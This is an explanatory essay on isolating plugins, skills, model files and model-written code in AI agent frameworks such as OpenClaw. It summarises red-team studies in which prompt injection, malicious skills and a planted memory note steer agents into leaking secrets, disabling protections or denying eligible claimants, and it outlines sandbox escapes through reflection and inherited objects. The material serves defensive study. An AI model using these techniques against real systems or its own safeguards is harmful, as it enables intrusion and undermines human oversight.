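# Containing semi-trusted AI components inside agent frameworks

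## Process, privilege and authority in an agent

An AI agent is a language model joined to software that acts on the model's output. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) uses the programmer Simon Willison's definition of an agent as something that runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal. A tool is a function such as a web search, a calendar query or a shell command. The agent framework is the program that runs the loop. It sends text to the model, parses the reply and carries out the requested actions. The part of the framework called the privileged code holds the passwords and keys, opens files and network connections, and enforces the user's rules.

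Frameworks also run things their developers neither wrote nor checked, such as marketplace plugins, scripts the model has just generated, and model files from public repositories. Each of these is a component, and so is the model's output, because the framework acts on it. Containment means limiting what a component can reach while still getting some use out of it. This problem is much older than language models. It arose, along with most of its vocabulary, when time-sharing computers first ran many people's programs side by side.

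### What a process protects, and from whom

A process is a running program and the resources the operating system has assigned to it, chiefly memory, open files and network connections. Its address space is the range of memory its instructions can refer to. Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 tutorial, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, describes the simplest hardware that keeps one program out of another's memory. A processor register holds two numbers, a base and a bound. The base is the lowest address the running program may use, and the bound is the number of locations beyond the base that it may also use. A circuit on the path to memory checks every reference against that range.

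A further bit, the privileged state bit, stops the program from loading a wider range into the register. The register accepts a new value only while the bit is on, and only the supervisor, now called the kernel, runs with it on. An ordinary program can turn the bit on only with an instruction that, in the same step, transfers control to the supervisor at a fixed entry point. Current processors use tables of small memory pages instead of a single range, but the same kind of bit ensures that only the supervisor can change those tables.

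The circuit compares an address with a range, regardless of which function issued the instruction or who wrote that function. Any native code in the process (machine instructions that the processor executes directly) can therefore read every byte the process can read, including a password in another module's variable. Marking the variable "private" in the source does not prevent this, because the compiler enforces that rule and machine code does not have to go through the compiler.

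Access to resources outside memory works similarly. When a process tries to open a file, the kernel on an ordinary desktop system checks the user account the process runs under, and all the code in the process runs under the same account. *Paradigm Regained*, a 2003 paper on access control by Miller and Shapiro, uses the card game Solitaire as an example. Solitaire needs only a window, mouse and keyboard events, and perhaps one file for a saved game, but it can do everything its user can. It could search the user's email for interesting items and sell them without breaking any of the operating system's rules.

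### One turn of the loop

Suppose that a mail assistant runs as one process on someone's laptop. The process holds a mail token (a string that the mail provider accepts in place of a password) and an API key (a string that identifies a paying customer to the company hosting the model). It can also start a shell. Into the same process the framework has loaded a plugin that summarises mail, written by a stranger. The arrangement is an ordinary one; OpenClaw's *Plugin internals*, the documentation of a popular open-source framework, describes native plugins that load in-process. The user types: "What did my landlord want this week?" In outline, following the algorithm that Pirch and colleagues give, this happens:

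1. The framework collects the conversation so far, its stored notes and a description of each tool, and puts them in a list with the user's question.
2. It sends the list to the model. The reply contains a structured request: the name of the mail-search tool, with "landlord" as its argument.
3. The framework parses the request, finds the function of that name and calls it. The function uses the mail token to fetch three messages, and the framework appends them to the list.
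4. It sends the longer list to the model. This time the reply requests the summariser. The framework calls the plugin with the three messages and appends the string that comes back.
5. The model's next reply contains an answer and no request, so the loop stops and the framework shows the answer to the user.

Anthropic's *How tool use works* tells developers that "The model never runs anything on its own." In Anthropic's interface, the model's reply includes a `tool_use` block requesting an operation, and the developer's code performs it and returns a `tool_result`.

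During inference, software converts text into a sequence of integers (tokens), multiplies them through large arrays of weights and gets a probability for each possible next token. *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) describes a model in isolation as a function from numbers to numbers, with no side effects and no persistent state. A model can output a command to erase a disk, but the disk is unaffected unless another program passes the command to a shell.

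A component's authority is everything it can bring about, either directly or by getting other code to act for it. A model gains authority through the code that loads it and the code that acts on its output. The loader reads a large file of uncertain origin with the full rights of its process. If the file exploits a bug in the loader, or its format allows it to carry code, the damage is done before the model produces its first token. (In the mail assistant the model is remote, so this risk sits with the hosting company.) For the code that acts on the output, Li and colleagues count four additions that turned text predictors into agents: a loop that feeds results back, a fixed interface for calling tools, files and notes that outlast a session, and installable extensions with schedules and background tasks. All four are conventional software, so a programmer can put limits in any of them. They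 find that agents have few internal limits by default, and that the model's output runs with the user's full authority. Approval prompts and sandboxes around the whole agent reduce that authority but do not divide it among the agent's components.

### The summariser with no containment

The plugin's job is to take in the text of some messages and give back a string. If it is native code in the framework's process and nothing restrains it, it can also:

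- copy the mail token out of memory and use it, then or later and from any machine, for whatever the token permits, which may include sending and deleting mail;
- copy the API key and run up charges on the user's account;
- read the whole conversation, along with the results of every other tool;
- start a shell and read, change or delete any file the user can, or install a program that starts at the next login;
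- open a network connection and send all of this somewhere;
- overwrite the framework's own data and functions, such as the log or the check that requests the user's confirmation;
- return a "summary" that contains instructions, in the hope that the model will follow them and request a different tool.

The final item needs no access to memory, files or the network. The plugin does it through its intended function, so measures that would stop all the other items do not stop it.

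A promise such as "nobody but the mail-search function uses the mail token" depends on the trusted computing base, which NIST's *trusted computing base (TCB)* entry defines as all the protection mechanisms in a system, in hardware, firmware and software, that together enforce a security policy. Here the stranger's plugin and every library in the process are in practice part of that base, because any of them can break the promise. Containment tries to remove them from the base. What remains has to be small because, as Saltzer and Schroeder point out, unwanted access paths do not show up in normal use and somebody has to find them by line-by-line inspection.

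### Semi-trusted components

In this field, a trusted component is one whose misbehaviour would break the security guarantee, whether or not anyone has reason to trust it. A hostile component is one that an adversary wrote or controls. Most plugins are neither. The user expects the summariser to be useful and benign, and is probably right, but it may have a bug, an attacker may have tampered with its latest update, and it reads text from anyone who knows the user's address. Such a component is semi-trusted, and it is sensible to run it with limited authority.

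A semi-trusted component still needs a strict boundary, because a security guarantee must cover everything the component could do, however unlikely. If a summariser has a memory error in the code that unpacks attachments, for example, a crafted message can make it execute the sender's instructions, however good its developer's intentions were. If the component is or contains a model, a prompt injection (text in the input that the model treats as instructions) can achieve much the same without a bug. Pirch and colleagues therefore treat the language model as completely untrusted, and they do not expect anyone to make models resistant to such manipulation in the foreseeable future. OpenAI's *Security & Privacy* guidance likewise advises plugin developers to assume that prompt injection and malicious input will arrive. Operating systems have worked on this assumption for decades, but Li and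 colleagues observe that agents were developed on the opposite one, with the model treated as a cooperative part of the program.

Miller and Shapiro fairly object that treating every program as hostile, though safe, ignores programs whose purpose is to enforce security. It led earlier researchers to declare some policies impossible that a few lines of well-behaved intermediary code can enforce. The worst-case assumption should therefore apply to the component, but not to the small piece of privileged code between it and the mail token, which we can read and judge by what it does. Partial trust still matters when the user decides what to give the component. A person might accept a small risk of leakage and let a reputable summariser see the landlord's letters, but would not show them to a known thief.

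### Two questions: isolation and authority

The list of the summariser's powers mixes two problems that need separate answers. The first is isolation, which concerns whether the component can read or write the privileged code's memory. The second is authority, which concerns what the component can do through the calls it is allowed to make.

Memory isolation and limits on calls can each fail while the other holds. If the summariser runs in a separate process, it cannot touch the framework's memory. But if it also has a host function (a function of the privileged code that a contained component may call) that runs any shell command, the user gains almost nothing from this perfect isolation. Limits on calls depend on isolation. A plugin in the shared address space that is offered no functions has no authority on paper, but it can read the token straight out of memory.

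A component's authority can also exceed what a table of permissions shows. In an example from Miller and Shapiro, Alice has permission to read a file and Bob does not, but Alice sends Bob copies. Bob therefore has the authority to read the file through Alice's behaviour, even without permission. The summariser is in a similar position. It may have no permission to send mail, but its output goes to a model whose output goes to code that can. How much authority the summariser has over mail depends on how readily the model follows instructions in a summary and on what the framework checks before sending.

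Much of the trouble comes from authority that a program exercises without selecting it, which Miller, Yee and Shapiro call ambient authority in *Capability Myths Demolished*. Their example is the Unix function `open()`. The caller supplies a file name but no credential, and the call succeeds or fails depending on who is running the program. They compare this to a building whose doors have no keys and open automatically for approved people.

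Comparing two common commands shows the alternative. The command `cp a.txt b.txt` passes two names to the copying program, which must open the files itself and therefore needs the right to open any file the user might name. With `cat < a.txt > b.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes on two file descriptors, which are handles to those particular files. Miller and Shapiro note that `cat` still runs with all the user's authority, but it needs only the two handles for this job. Such a handle is close to a capability, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. Some programming languages base their entire security model on capabilities.

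### Least privilege and the confused deputy

Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of least privilege is that every program should run with the smallest set of privileges it needs to finish its job. They justify it mainly as a way to limit the damage from accidents and errors, and add that it leaves fewer programs to audit when somebody suspects misuse. The summariser needs only the text of the chosen messages, some memory and processor time, and a way to return a string. Saltzer and Schroeder recommend denying access by default, because a mistake in a list of permissions usually causes a refusal that someone notices, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions silently allows access. They also say the system should check every access, by every route. Li and colleagues found that coding agents fall short of this, since a file write that the file tool refuses can go through the shell.

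Least privilege for the component does not protect the user from the privileged code itself. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) gives the classic example, a "nearly true" story about the time-sharing company Tymshare. A compiler there was stored in a directory called SYSX and recorded usage statistics in a file in the same directory, so the staff gave it permission to write files in SYSX. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the company's billing file, which was also in SYSX. The user had no permission to write there, but the compiler did, and it overwrote the billing records with the debugging output.

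Hardy argues that no line of the compiler was at fault. The code that wrote debugging output was correct until the staff added the licence. The compiler could not simply reject names in SYSX, because some users had legitimate access to that directory. It held authority from both its licence and the user who ran it, and had no way to specify which one applied to a given file. Tymshare added a system call to switch between the two, but soon had applications that needed more than two. Hardy preferred to have the user pass the compiler a capability for the output file, which combines the file's name with the right to write to it. A user with no right to write to the billing file would then have no capability for it to pass.

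An agent framework is constantly in the compiler's position. If the summariser plugin is allowed to suggest a file name for saving an attachment, it can suggest the name of the file that lists who may log in to the laptop. If the privileged code then writes to that file with its own rights, the plugin has changed the file without having access to it. Running the plugin in a separate process would not prevent this.

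### The confinement problem

Even under least privilege, the summariser needs access to the landlord's letters. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) considers whether anything can stop such a program from passing on what it reads. A customer calls a service and has to give it data, and the task is to ensure that the service cannot transmit the data to the service's owner. Lampson considers a leak worse than bad work, because bad work leaves evidence in the output and a leak generally leaves none. The service can keep the data in its own memory until its owner calls, write a file where the owner will find it, or send the owner a message. It can also encode a few bits in the bill, or open and close a file in a pattern that another program detects by trying to open the same file. It can alternate between heavy computing and heavy disk use, so that a program running at the same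 time reads the signal from the speed of the machine. Lampson called this last kind of route a covert channel, meaning one that nobody intended for communication at all. Channels that leak data through timing and other physical effects are now usually called side channels.

A program is confined if it keeps no memory between calls and calls no other program. Lampson concedes that this is impractical, since even time-slicing the processor counts as a call on the supervisor. In a workable version, any untrusted program that the confined program calls must also be confined, and the supervisor, which nobody can confine, must be trustworthy. The caller must also determine everything the confined program puts into its legitimate and covert channels, and the supervisor must enforce this, if necessary by slowing the program down. Where the overhead of enforcement is too high, Lampson suggests limiting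 how much information the channels can carry.

The framework can meet the first of these demands for the summariser by starting a fresh copy of the plugin for each call and giving it no files or network access. The summary is a legitimate channel, like Lampson's bill, but it is harder to control because the user needs the plugin to write it and so cannot determine its contents in advance. If the framework later puts the summary into a web search or an outgoing message, it also sends anything the plugin hid in the wording. A length limit would be a ceiling of the kind Lampson proposed, but a useful summary would still have room for a password.

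## What shares the privileged process in current frameworks

The mail assistant had one stranger's plugin in its process. Frameworks in daily use also take in shell commands, generated scripts, model files and written instructions. OpenClaw, which Peter Steinberger released in November 2025, is a good main example because it is popular and its maintainers state openly what they trust. Pirch and colleagues note that it was the sixth most-starred project on GitHub by May 2026.

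OpenClaw's central program, the Gateway, is the privileged code. According to OpenClaw's overview of its trust boundary, the Gateway holds the chat connections, configuration and credentials, and applies the policy on what the agent may do. Sandboxing is off by default, and shell commands run on the Gateway's own machine without a prompt. The operator (the person who runs the Gateway) can instead run tools in a container, on another machine, or in OpenShell, a separate sandbox product. The standard container has no network and a read-only root file system. The operator can also use cloud workers, temporary machines that do a session's coding work. A cloud worker may call only a fixed list of Gateway functions, its credentials expire after ten minutes, and it gets the model's replies through the Gateway, so it never holds the model key. These options move tools and sessions out of the Gateway,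 but native plugins still run inside it.

### Tool calls and model-written code

Through tool calls, the model can do anything the available functions can do with any arguments they accept. Unless the operator changes the settings described in OpenClaw's *Tool and agent permissions*, OpenClaw's file tools can read outside the agent's workspace folder, and an agent with the message tool can write to any conversation on any connected chat service. The tool that applies patches to files is restricted to the workspace by default, but the shell is not.

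The maintainers do not trust the model with all of this. *GHSA-cwj3-vqpp-pmxr* (2026), an advisory in the open-source vulnerability database OSV, concerns a guard meant to stop the agent from changing the Gateway's configuration. The guard was a list of forbidden settings. In version 2026.4.23, the maintainers replaced it with a short list of permitted settings because they consider the model "not a trusted principal". The current version of the tool cannot write configuration at all.

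A model can also write a program for the framework to run. The riskiest way to run it is in the framework's own interpreter. LangChain, a widely used Python framework, once had a component that passed model-written Python to `exec`, a function that runs a string as code in the current process. Such code can import any library and read any variable, so it has the same access as a native plugin. *Don't Let the Claw Grip Your Hand* (2026) lists the resulting flaw, CVE-2023-44467, among those that let attackers run code remotely through prompt injection. Restricted interpreters such as Monty are meant to make it safe to run model-written code inside the framework's process.

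*Architectural Design Decisions in AI Agent Harnesses* (Hu, 2026) examined 70 publicly available agent projects and found that 17% had no isolation, 45% used a child process, 31% a container and 7% WebAssembly. A child process, the most common form of isolation, keeps a script out of the framework's memory but protects little else, because it normally runs under the same user account and inherits the parent's environment variables, where many programs keep their keys. OpenClaw's shell commands run this way by default, and they can also read the folder that holds the Gateway's configuration.

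### Plugins and hooks

An OpenClaw plugin is a JavaScript or TypeScript module that the Gateway loads and registers by calling its `register` function with an object named `api`. The plugin uses this object to add tools, network handlers, background services and hooks, which are functions that the framework calls at fixed points in its work. According to OpenClaw's plugin documentation, a plugin has the same trust boundary as core code, a bug in it can crash the Gateway, and a malicious plugin is equivalent to arbitrary code execution inside the process. The `api` object does not confine the plugin, because the module can directly use the file and network functions that the JavaScript runtime offers to all code.

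OpenClaw's *Secure file operations* describes the framework's file checks as protection for trusted Gateway code that handles untrusted paths, including paths from plugins. A checked function can refuse a bad path that a plugin passes to it, but the checks don't run if the plugin opens the file itself.

The operator's main chance to stop a bad plugin is before it loads. Installing or updating a plugin already runs code. OpenClaw warns about new sources, such as an arbitrary package or code repository, but treats packages from its own marketplace, ClawHub, as trusted. It does not block dangerous code on its own during installation, but the operator can supply a command that inspects each package and allows it, warns about it or blocks it. The operator can also use an allowlist of plugins, but it works by name and does not verify where the code came from or determine which of two copies with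 the same name will load.

Loading rules can have bugs too. *CVE-2026-43571* (2026), published by Croatia's computer emergency team, CERT.hr, describes one in OpenClaw versions before 2026.4.10. While setting up a chat channel, OpenClaw could choose a plugin from the workspace folder over the bundled plugin it imitated, so anyone who could put a malicious plugin in that folder could get it past the trust check. With no further barrier after loading, such a bug can give an attacker control of the entire process.

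GitLab's *GHSA-ff98-w8hj-qrxf* (March 3, 2026) is an advisory on `runCommandWithTimeout`, a function that OpenClaw plugins use to run commands on the host. It classes the problem as command injection, rates it 5.3 out of 10 and gives 2026.2.19 as the fixed version, but its stated purpose is to clarify that plugins run in-process as trusted code and that this trust covers command execution. Plugins remain unconfined after the update. OpenClaw's security policy counts them as part of the trusted computing base and expects them to read files and run host commands.

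In the plugin documentation, a "capability" is a type of feature that a plugin registers, such as speech, web search or image generation. This may confuse readers who know the term from the security literature. The Gateway uses this registration to choose which plugin to call for a feature, but registration doesn't restrict what the plugin can do. The documentation calls a plugin "non-capability" if it adds tools or services without registering any of these features, but such a plugin still has all the authority of the process.

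### Model files and inference libraries

If the framework runs a model locally, the weights file it loads may be in a format that can carry code. The best-known example is pickle, Python's standard format for saving objects, which older PyTorch model files use. A pickle file is a series of instructions for rebuilding an object. One instruction can import a function by name, and another can call it with arguments stored in the file. This is useful for rebuilding complicated objects, but it also lets an attacker write a file that runs a shell command during loading, with all the rights of the process.

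PyTorch's `weights_only` option restricts loading to a list of approved types and functions, and has been the default since version 2.6. It is safer than unrestricted loading, but in 2025 researchers found a way to run code despite the option in versions before 2.6. The safetensors format avoids the problem more thoroughly. Its files contain a header listing the name, type, shape and position of each array, followed by the raw numbers, with no instructions to import or call anything.

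Even a file in a data-only format can exploit a bug in the program that reads it. Inference libraries are mostly native code, written in C or C++ for speed. If such a library uses a false length from a file's header without checking it, it may write past the end of a buffer, and a carefully made file can turn that into code execution. Native code is also hard to unload. In OpenClaw, a native library stays in the Gateway's memory until the process exits, even after OpenClaw has dropped the module that loaded it. An operator who suspects a native plugin should therefore restart the Gateway, not just disable the plugin.

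Frameworks also rebuild objects from stored data in other places, and similar flaws turn up there. Callahan, in *Agent Frameworks Fail Security Boundary Test*, reports that in August 2026 Yarden Porat and Shahar Tal of Check Point Research disclosed 11 vulnerabilities in six frameworks, including LangChain and Microsoft's AutoGen. The vulnerabilities included two types that long predate agents, unsafe deserialization (the general name for the pickle problem) and path traversal, in which a file name containing steps such as `../` leads out of the permitted folder.

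### Skills

A skill is a folder with a text file, `SKILL.md`, that tells the model how to do a task. It may also contain scripts and programs. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (2026) describes how OpenClaw puts the text into the model's context at the start of a session and trusts it as much as instructions from the operator. The text cannot access memory or files directly, but if the model follows it, it can reach whatever the model's tools reach. With OpenClaw's defaults, that includes the shell.

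Skills are hard to review because, as Pirch and colleagues point out, the model chooses the tools at run time, and the same text can lead to different calls depending on the model and the rest of the conversation. Marketplaces offer over a million skills, and in February 2026 the malware-scanning service VirusTotal documented hundreds of malicious ones. OpenClaw advises users to treat skill folders as trusted code and restrict who can change them. OpenClaw can pick up an edited `SKILL.md` mid-session, so anyone with write access to the folder can change the agent's instructions while it works.

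### The case for plugins in the process

The maintainers' main argument is that each Gateway serves a single operator or a team whose members trust each other, as OpenClaw's *Security trust model* requires. People who do not trust each other should run separate Gateways, preferably under separate user accounts or on separate machines. An operator can already run any program on the computer, so the maintainers regard shell access without prompts as a deliberate convenience. On this view, a plugin is another program the operator chose to install. A security report must show that something crossed a boundary, for instance by loading without permission, and bad behaviour by an installed plugin does not qualify.

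The usual engineering reasons for running components in the privileged process are speed and simplicity. A function call within a process takes almost no time, while a call to another process has to copy its arguments and wait for the operating system to switch between the two. OpenClaw's plugins also give the Gateway live functions to call, such as hooks and handlers for streamed text. If the plugins ran in a separate process, the developers would need a message format for each of these functions and rules for what happens when the other process crashes.

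The overhead of crossing between processes hardly matters for a plugin that calls a remote model and waits seconds for a reply. Simplicity is a more serious benefit of sharing a process, especially for a young project with many outside contributors. The single-operator argument works well for hostile users but poorly for hostile code, because operators may trust themselves completely and still know nothing about the author of a plugin's latest update. Steinberger accepts the general danger, writing on OpenClaw's blog that "Nothing that can run tools, hold credentials and install plugins is safe by default." The maintainers also advise designing on the assumption that someone will manipulate the model, but they do not extend that assumption to plugins.

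### Four agents under attack

Pirch and colleagues tested how much protection OpenClaw and three similar agents provide in practice. They start from an analogy with operating systems, in which the model corresponds to a user, the framework to the kernel, tools to system calls, and skills to programs. The model's context corresponds to memory, files to storage, and timed jobs to the scheduler. They argue that a framework should stay secure whatever its model outputs, just as a kernel has to stay secure whatever its users do.

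In many of these agents, the loop, the tools and the file checks all run at the same privilege level, so the part that acts as the kernel lacks the hardware barrier that protects a real one. The model's context also has no equivalent of separate address spaces, because all four agents put trusted and untrusted text into one shared context, where the output of one tool can influence the next call.

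Pirch and colleagues chose agents with different designs. OpenClaw is feature-rich, while IronClaw is a security-focused reimplementation in Rust that runs many of its tools in WebAssembly. Nanobot has a core loop of fewer than 6,000 lines, and Nvidia's NemoClaw runs an unmodified OpenClaw inside a container with filtered network access. The assumed attacker knows the source code and default settings but has no direct access to the machine. Some attacks come from a peer, someone allowed to message the agent, and others from a malicious skill.

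Each agent ran in its own virtual machine, which was restored to a clean snapshot before every test. File and network activity was recorded from the operating system's kernel. An attack counted as successful if it worked at least once in three attempts. The agents mostly kept the recommended default settings, though Nanobot ran with the sandbox that its documentation recommends. The model was Qwen3.5-122B. The table shows how many of the applicable attacks succeeded against each agent.

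| Protection under attack | OpenClaw | IronClaw | Nanobot | NemoClaw |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Control over tool calls and downloaded code | 2 of 2 | 0 of 1 | 2 of 2 | 2 of 2 |
| Separation of users, skills and memory | 5 of 5 | 3 of 3 | 3 of 5 | 5 of 5 |
| Sandboxing of the host and the agent's own files | 5 of 5 | 1 of 5 | 0 of 5 | 1 of 5 |
| Limits on messages and web access | 2 of 2 | 2 of 2 | 2 of 2 | 1 of 2 |
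| Protection of logs and audits | 2 of 2 | 1 of 1 | 0 of 1 | 2 of 2 |
| Total | 16 of 16 | 7 of 12 | 7 of 15 | 11 of 16 |

Every attack worked on OpenClaw. A peer could make it rewrite its own code, print its environment variables and fetch a secret from the user's home folder. OpenClaw's security audit checked for calls to `eval`, which runs text as code, but detected them only when the parentheses were on the same line as `eval`.

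Sandboxing made the clearest difference. Nanobot's sandbox stopped all five attacks on the host and the agent's files. IronClaw's stopped four, but a peer could still get the agent to change its own configuration and disable security measures. NemoClaw's container also stopped four, and the fifth leaked only the system prompt, the standing instructions given to the model. But the container surrounds the whole agent and does not separate the users and skills inside it, so all five attacks that relied on this lack of separation succeeded.

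Two attacks worked on all four agents. In one, a user tells the agent a secret and another user asks for it. In the other, the attacker has the agent send an unsolicited message to a third person. Both use functions the agent is supposed to have, so a sandbox around its code does not help.

The choice of model mattered more for OpenClaw than the main results suggest. When Pirch and colleagues repeated the tests with GPT-5.5, only 5 of the 16 attacks on OpenClaw worked, though the researchers did not adapt their prompts to the new model. On IronClaw, 6 of the 7 attacks that had originally worked still did. A more careful model can therefore prevent many simple attacks, but its refusals are not a dependable boundary. Gemini 2.5 Pro refused to reveal another user's secret on IronClaw until the researchers added a simple prompt injection.

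The maintainers could reasonably object that much of this is expected behaviour. Eleven of the sixteen attacks come from a peer, and under OpenClaw's stated trust model, everyone who can message a tool-using agent shares its authority. OpenClaw therefore hasn't broken a promise, but an operator who adds the agent to a group chat may not have understood that the other members would share that authority. The study also doesn't test native plugins, the most powerful component. A malicious plugin in the Gateway would not need to manipulate a model to do harm.

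### Other frameworks

OpenClaw is not unusual in leaving protection to the operator. Hossain, Hossain and colleagues (2026), in *The Containment Gap*, audited LangChain, the OpenAI Agents SDK (OpenAI's toolkit for building agents) and AutoGPT, an early autonomous agent. They looked for six protections:

- a policy check between the model's plan and its execution;
- limits on the tools and arguments available in each session;
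- validation of anything written to long-term memory;
- checks wherever data passes from one stage of the loop to the next;
- authenticated messages between agents;
- monitoring that detects unusual behaviour and responds to it.

None of the three frameworks had any of these fully in place by default. In LangChain, developers could configure partial versions of four, using callbacks (functions the framework calls at certain steps), tool lists and tracing. It lacked memory validation and authenticated messages. The OpenAI Agents SDK had partial, configurable versions of five, including optional "guardrails" that check inputs and actions. AutoGPT had only human approval, which the audit counted as partial monitoring.

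The scores record whether a mechanism exists and are a poor measure of how well it works. The OpenAI toolkit failed on memory validation because it had no built-in memory to validate, not because it accepted poisoned entries. None of the six criteria covers whether plugins share an address space with the credentials, so a framework could pass the whole audit and still let a plugin read every key.

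Hossain and colleagues also built a LangChain agent that decided invented welfare claims. Partway through a run, they added one false policy note to its memory, an instruction to deny low-income applicants from one region. The agent then refused every eligible applicant from that region whom it had previously approved. The same happened with the larger models Claude Haiku 4.5 and GPT-4o. With a more complicated policy and Claude Sonnet 4.6, overall accuracy fell only from 100% to 92.5%, while wrongful refusals in the targeted region rose from none to 75%. A stored note can steer an agent much as a skill does, and an operator who monitors only overall accuracy may miss the effect on one group.

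In another test, the researchers made 100 hostile tool requests, such as attempts to read files outside the permitted folder. All of them succeeded until the researchers added a check on tool names and file paths. The check blocked all 100 and took about 0.13 milliseconds per call, so speed is a poor reason to leave such checks out. The researchers wrote it with these attacks in mind, however, so the result is weak evidence that it would stop attackers who adapt.

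A list of permitted tools does not solve the confused deputy problem. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines whether LangChain, LangGraph, the data-retrieval framework LlamaIndex and the payment company Stripe's agent toolkit authorise each call again, with its actual arguments, before carrying it out. Mellafe Zuvic argues that common defaults confuse making a tool available with authorising its use. For example, if a user lets an agent issue refunds, the framework may accept any refund the model requests, including one prompted by instructions in a customer's email.

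## Restricted interpreters for model-written code

With ordinary tool calls, each step that depends on an earlier result takes another turn of the agent loop, and all the intermediate output goes back to the model. Many developers now instead let the model write a short program that calls the tools. Pydantic's *Monty* traces the idea to Cloudflare (which calls it "code mode"), Anthropic, and Hugging Face's agent framework, smolagents.

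In a small example, Pydantic, a company best known for its Python data validation library, asked Claude Sonnet 4.5 to compare the weather in London and Paris. The model had three functions, which found a city's coordinates, got the temperature there, and described that temperature in words. It replied four times when using tool calls but only twice in code mode, once with a program and once with the answer. Code mode cut the time from 12.2 to 9.1 seconds and the cost from 1.9 to 1.7 cents. In another example, the model wrote a program that extracted prices from web pages too long to fit in its context.

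Code mode helps more on longer tasks. In October 2026, Pydantic tested eight models in five applications for *A secure place to run your agent's code*. On long tasks, code mode used 9% to 70% fewer tokens. The success rate rose from 14% to 58% for GPT-6 Luna and from 86% to 92% for GPT-6 Astra, while one model succeeded every time with either method. Pydantic sells a service that runs model-written programs and has not released its test code, so these figures are better evidence for the direction of the effect than for its size.

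The framework needs somewhere to run the program. One option is to take a full language such as Python and block its dangerous parts. Another is to write a small interpreter that has no dangerous operations to block. (A compiler can also reject unsafe programs before they run, as in the research system TACIT.)

### Why filtering a full language fails

A filter lets the program use some names and refuses others, such as `open` and `import`. This may not be enough in Python or JavaScript, because both have reflection, a set of features that let a program examine its own objects. In Python, every value links to its class, classes link to other classes, and functions link to the variables of the module that defined them. A program can follow these links from a harmless object, such as a number, to one that can open files, without using a forbidden name. The filter has to block every such route,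 including any that a new version of the language adds.

Python's standard library once had a module called `rexec` that ran code with a restricted set of built-in functions. Python's developers disabled it in Python 2.3, released in 2003, because it had known holes that they could not readily fix. Victor Stinner, a Python core developer, later tried again with pysandbox and abandoned it in 2013. Stinner concluded that reflection gave code too many ways to escape, and that the sandbox was secure only if the entire Python interpreter, a huge body of C code, had no exploitable bugs. Stinner recommended running the whole interpreter inside an external sandbox instead.

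Agent frameworks have also tried restricted interpreters. The local executor in smolagents checks each operation in the model's program, but the program still works with ordinary Python objects, whose links to other objects can lead out of the interpreter. Most of these links have names that begin and end with double underscores. OSV's *CVE-2025-9959* (2025) describes an escape that was possible because the executor's checks on such names were incomplete. To use the flaw, an attacker would first need a prompt injection that made the model write the malicious code. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-542* (2026) covers a separate escape from the same executor, with a severity of 9.9 out of 10.

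A list of permitted items works only if everything on it is harmless. Agenta, a platform for developing language-model applications, ran its users' code through a filter called RestrictedPython and put the numerical library numpy on the permitted list. According to DevGuard's *PYSEC-2026-6* (2026), this let any logged-in user escape the restrictions. Numpy can also read files and load native libraries, but Agenta's developers had treated it as a library for arithmetic.

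Programs could escape Terrarium, a sandbox from the AI company Cohere, through JavaScript objects. Terrarium ran Python in Pyodide, a version of the standard Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly, a format designed for confined code. Pyodide runs inside a JavaScript engine and lets Python code use JavaScript objects. Cohere's developers supplied a dummy version of the browser's `document` object, apparently assuming that it had only the properties they gave it. But an ordinary JavaScript object also inherits properties from a shared base object. CERT/CC, which coordinates the disclosure of software vulnerabilities, traced the escape to these inherited links, which let a program reach powerful functions in the surrounding runtime and then run commands as root inside Terrarium's container. The Hacker News (2026) gives the severity as 9.3 out of 10.

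Pydantic had the same kind of trouble with an earlier tool of its own, mcp-run-python. It also used Pyodide, and GitLab's *CVE-2026-25905* (2026) reports that it placed no restriction on the bridge between Python and JavaScript. In both tools, WebAssembly confined the Python interpreter's memory, but the program could leave through objects on the JavaScript side. (V8 isolates, which give each JavaScript program a separate heap, do not depend on filtering objects in this way.)

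### How Monty runs a program

Monty is a Python interpreter that Pydantic wrote from scratch in Rust, using no part of CPython, the standard implementation. None of the Python operations it implements opens a file, connects to a network or starts another program. A program running in Monty can still follow links between objects, but no object inside the interpreter would give it these abilities.

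Suppose that the model in the mail assistant writes this program, and that the framework supplies the value of `week_start`:

```python
messages = search_mail("landlord")
recent = [m for m in messages if m["sent"] >= week_start]
[m["text"] for m in recent]
```

Monty handles it as follows:

1. A parser, which Monty borrows from the Python code checker Ruff, turns the text into a tree of expressions. If the framework asks for it, a type checker then compares the program with a description of the available functions.
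2. Monty compiles the tree to bytecode, a list of simple instructions for the interpreter's main loop.
3. The loop executes these instructions until it reaches `search_mail`, which the program does not define. Monty looks for the name among the host functions that the framework has supplied.
4. At the call, Monty suspends the program and gives the framework the function's name and its argument, "landlord".
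5. The framework's privileged code decides whether to allow the call. If it does, it runs the real function, using the mail token, and returns the messages.
6. Monty converts the messages into its own objects and resumes the program, which picks out the recent ones. The value of the last line goes back to the framework.

The mail token never enters the interpreter, and the messages the program discards never reach the model. Unless the framework supplies access, the program cannot use files, environment variables, the network or other programs. Pydantic's *Security Model* makes an exception for the clock and random numbers, which are available by default. Pydantic calls the clock a weak capability because a program can use it to measure elapsed time, which helps in reading some side channels. The framework can prevent this by freezing the clock.

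Every outside effect involves a pause, so the framework can run its checks then. An episode of the podcast Talk Python with Monty's creator, Samuel Colvin, gives the examples of inspecting a web address before fetching it and blocking requests to the local machine. But a framework that already checks ordinary tool calls may run those checks elsewhere. Microsoft's *agent-framework-monty 1.0.0b261112* (2026), a beta package that adds Monty to Microsoft's agent framework, comes with a warning that calls from generated code bypass part of the agent's usual handling of functions. The package therefore does not support FIDES, Microsoft's system for controlling how information flows through an agent.

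Monty can also write a suspended program's complete state to a few kilobytes, so an agent can wait days for a person's approval and then continue, even on another machine. The stored state needs protection because Monty does not check who produced it. The state includes the program's resource limits and can request calls to host functions, so someone who can edit the saved file may be able to change what the program does after the approval.

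### Files, objects and resource limits

If a program needs files, the framework can mount a folder, making it available under a virtual path such as `/data`. The framework can allow read-only access, full access, or use an overlay that keeps changes in memory and discards them after the run. Monty passes each file operation to code outside the interpreter, which carries it out, the same way it handles a call to a host function.

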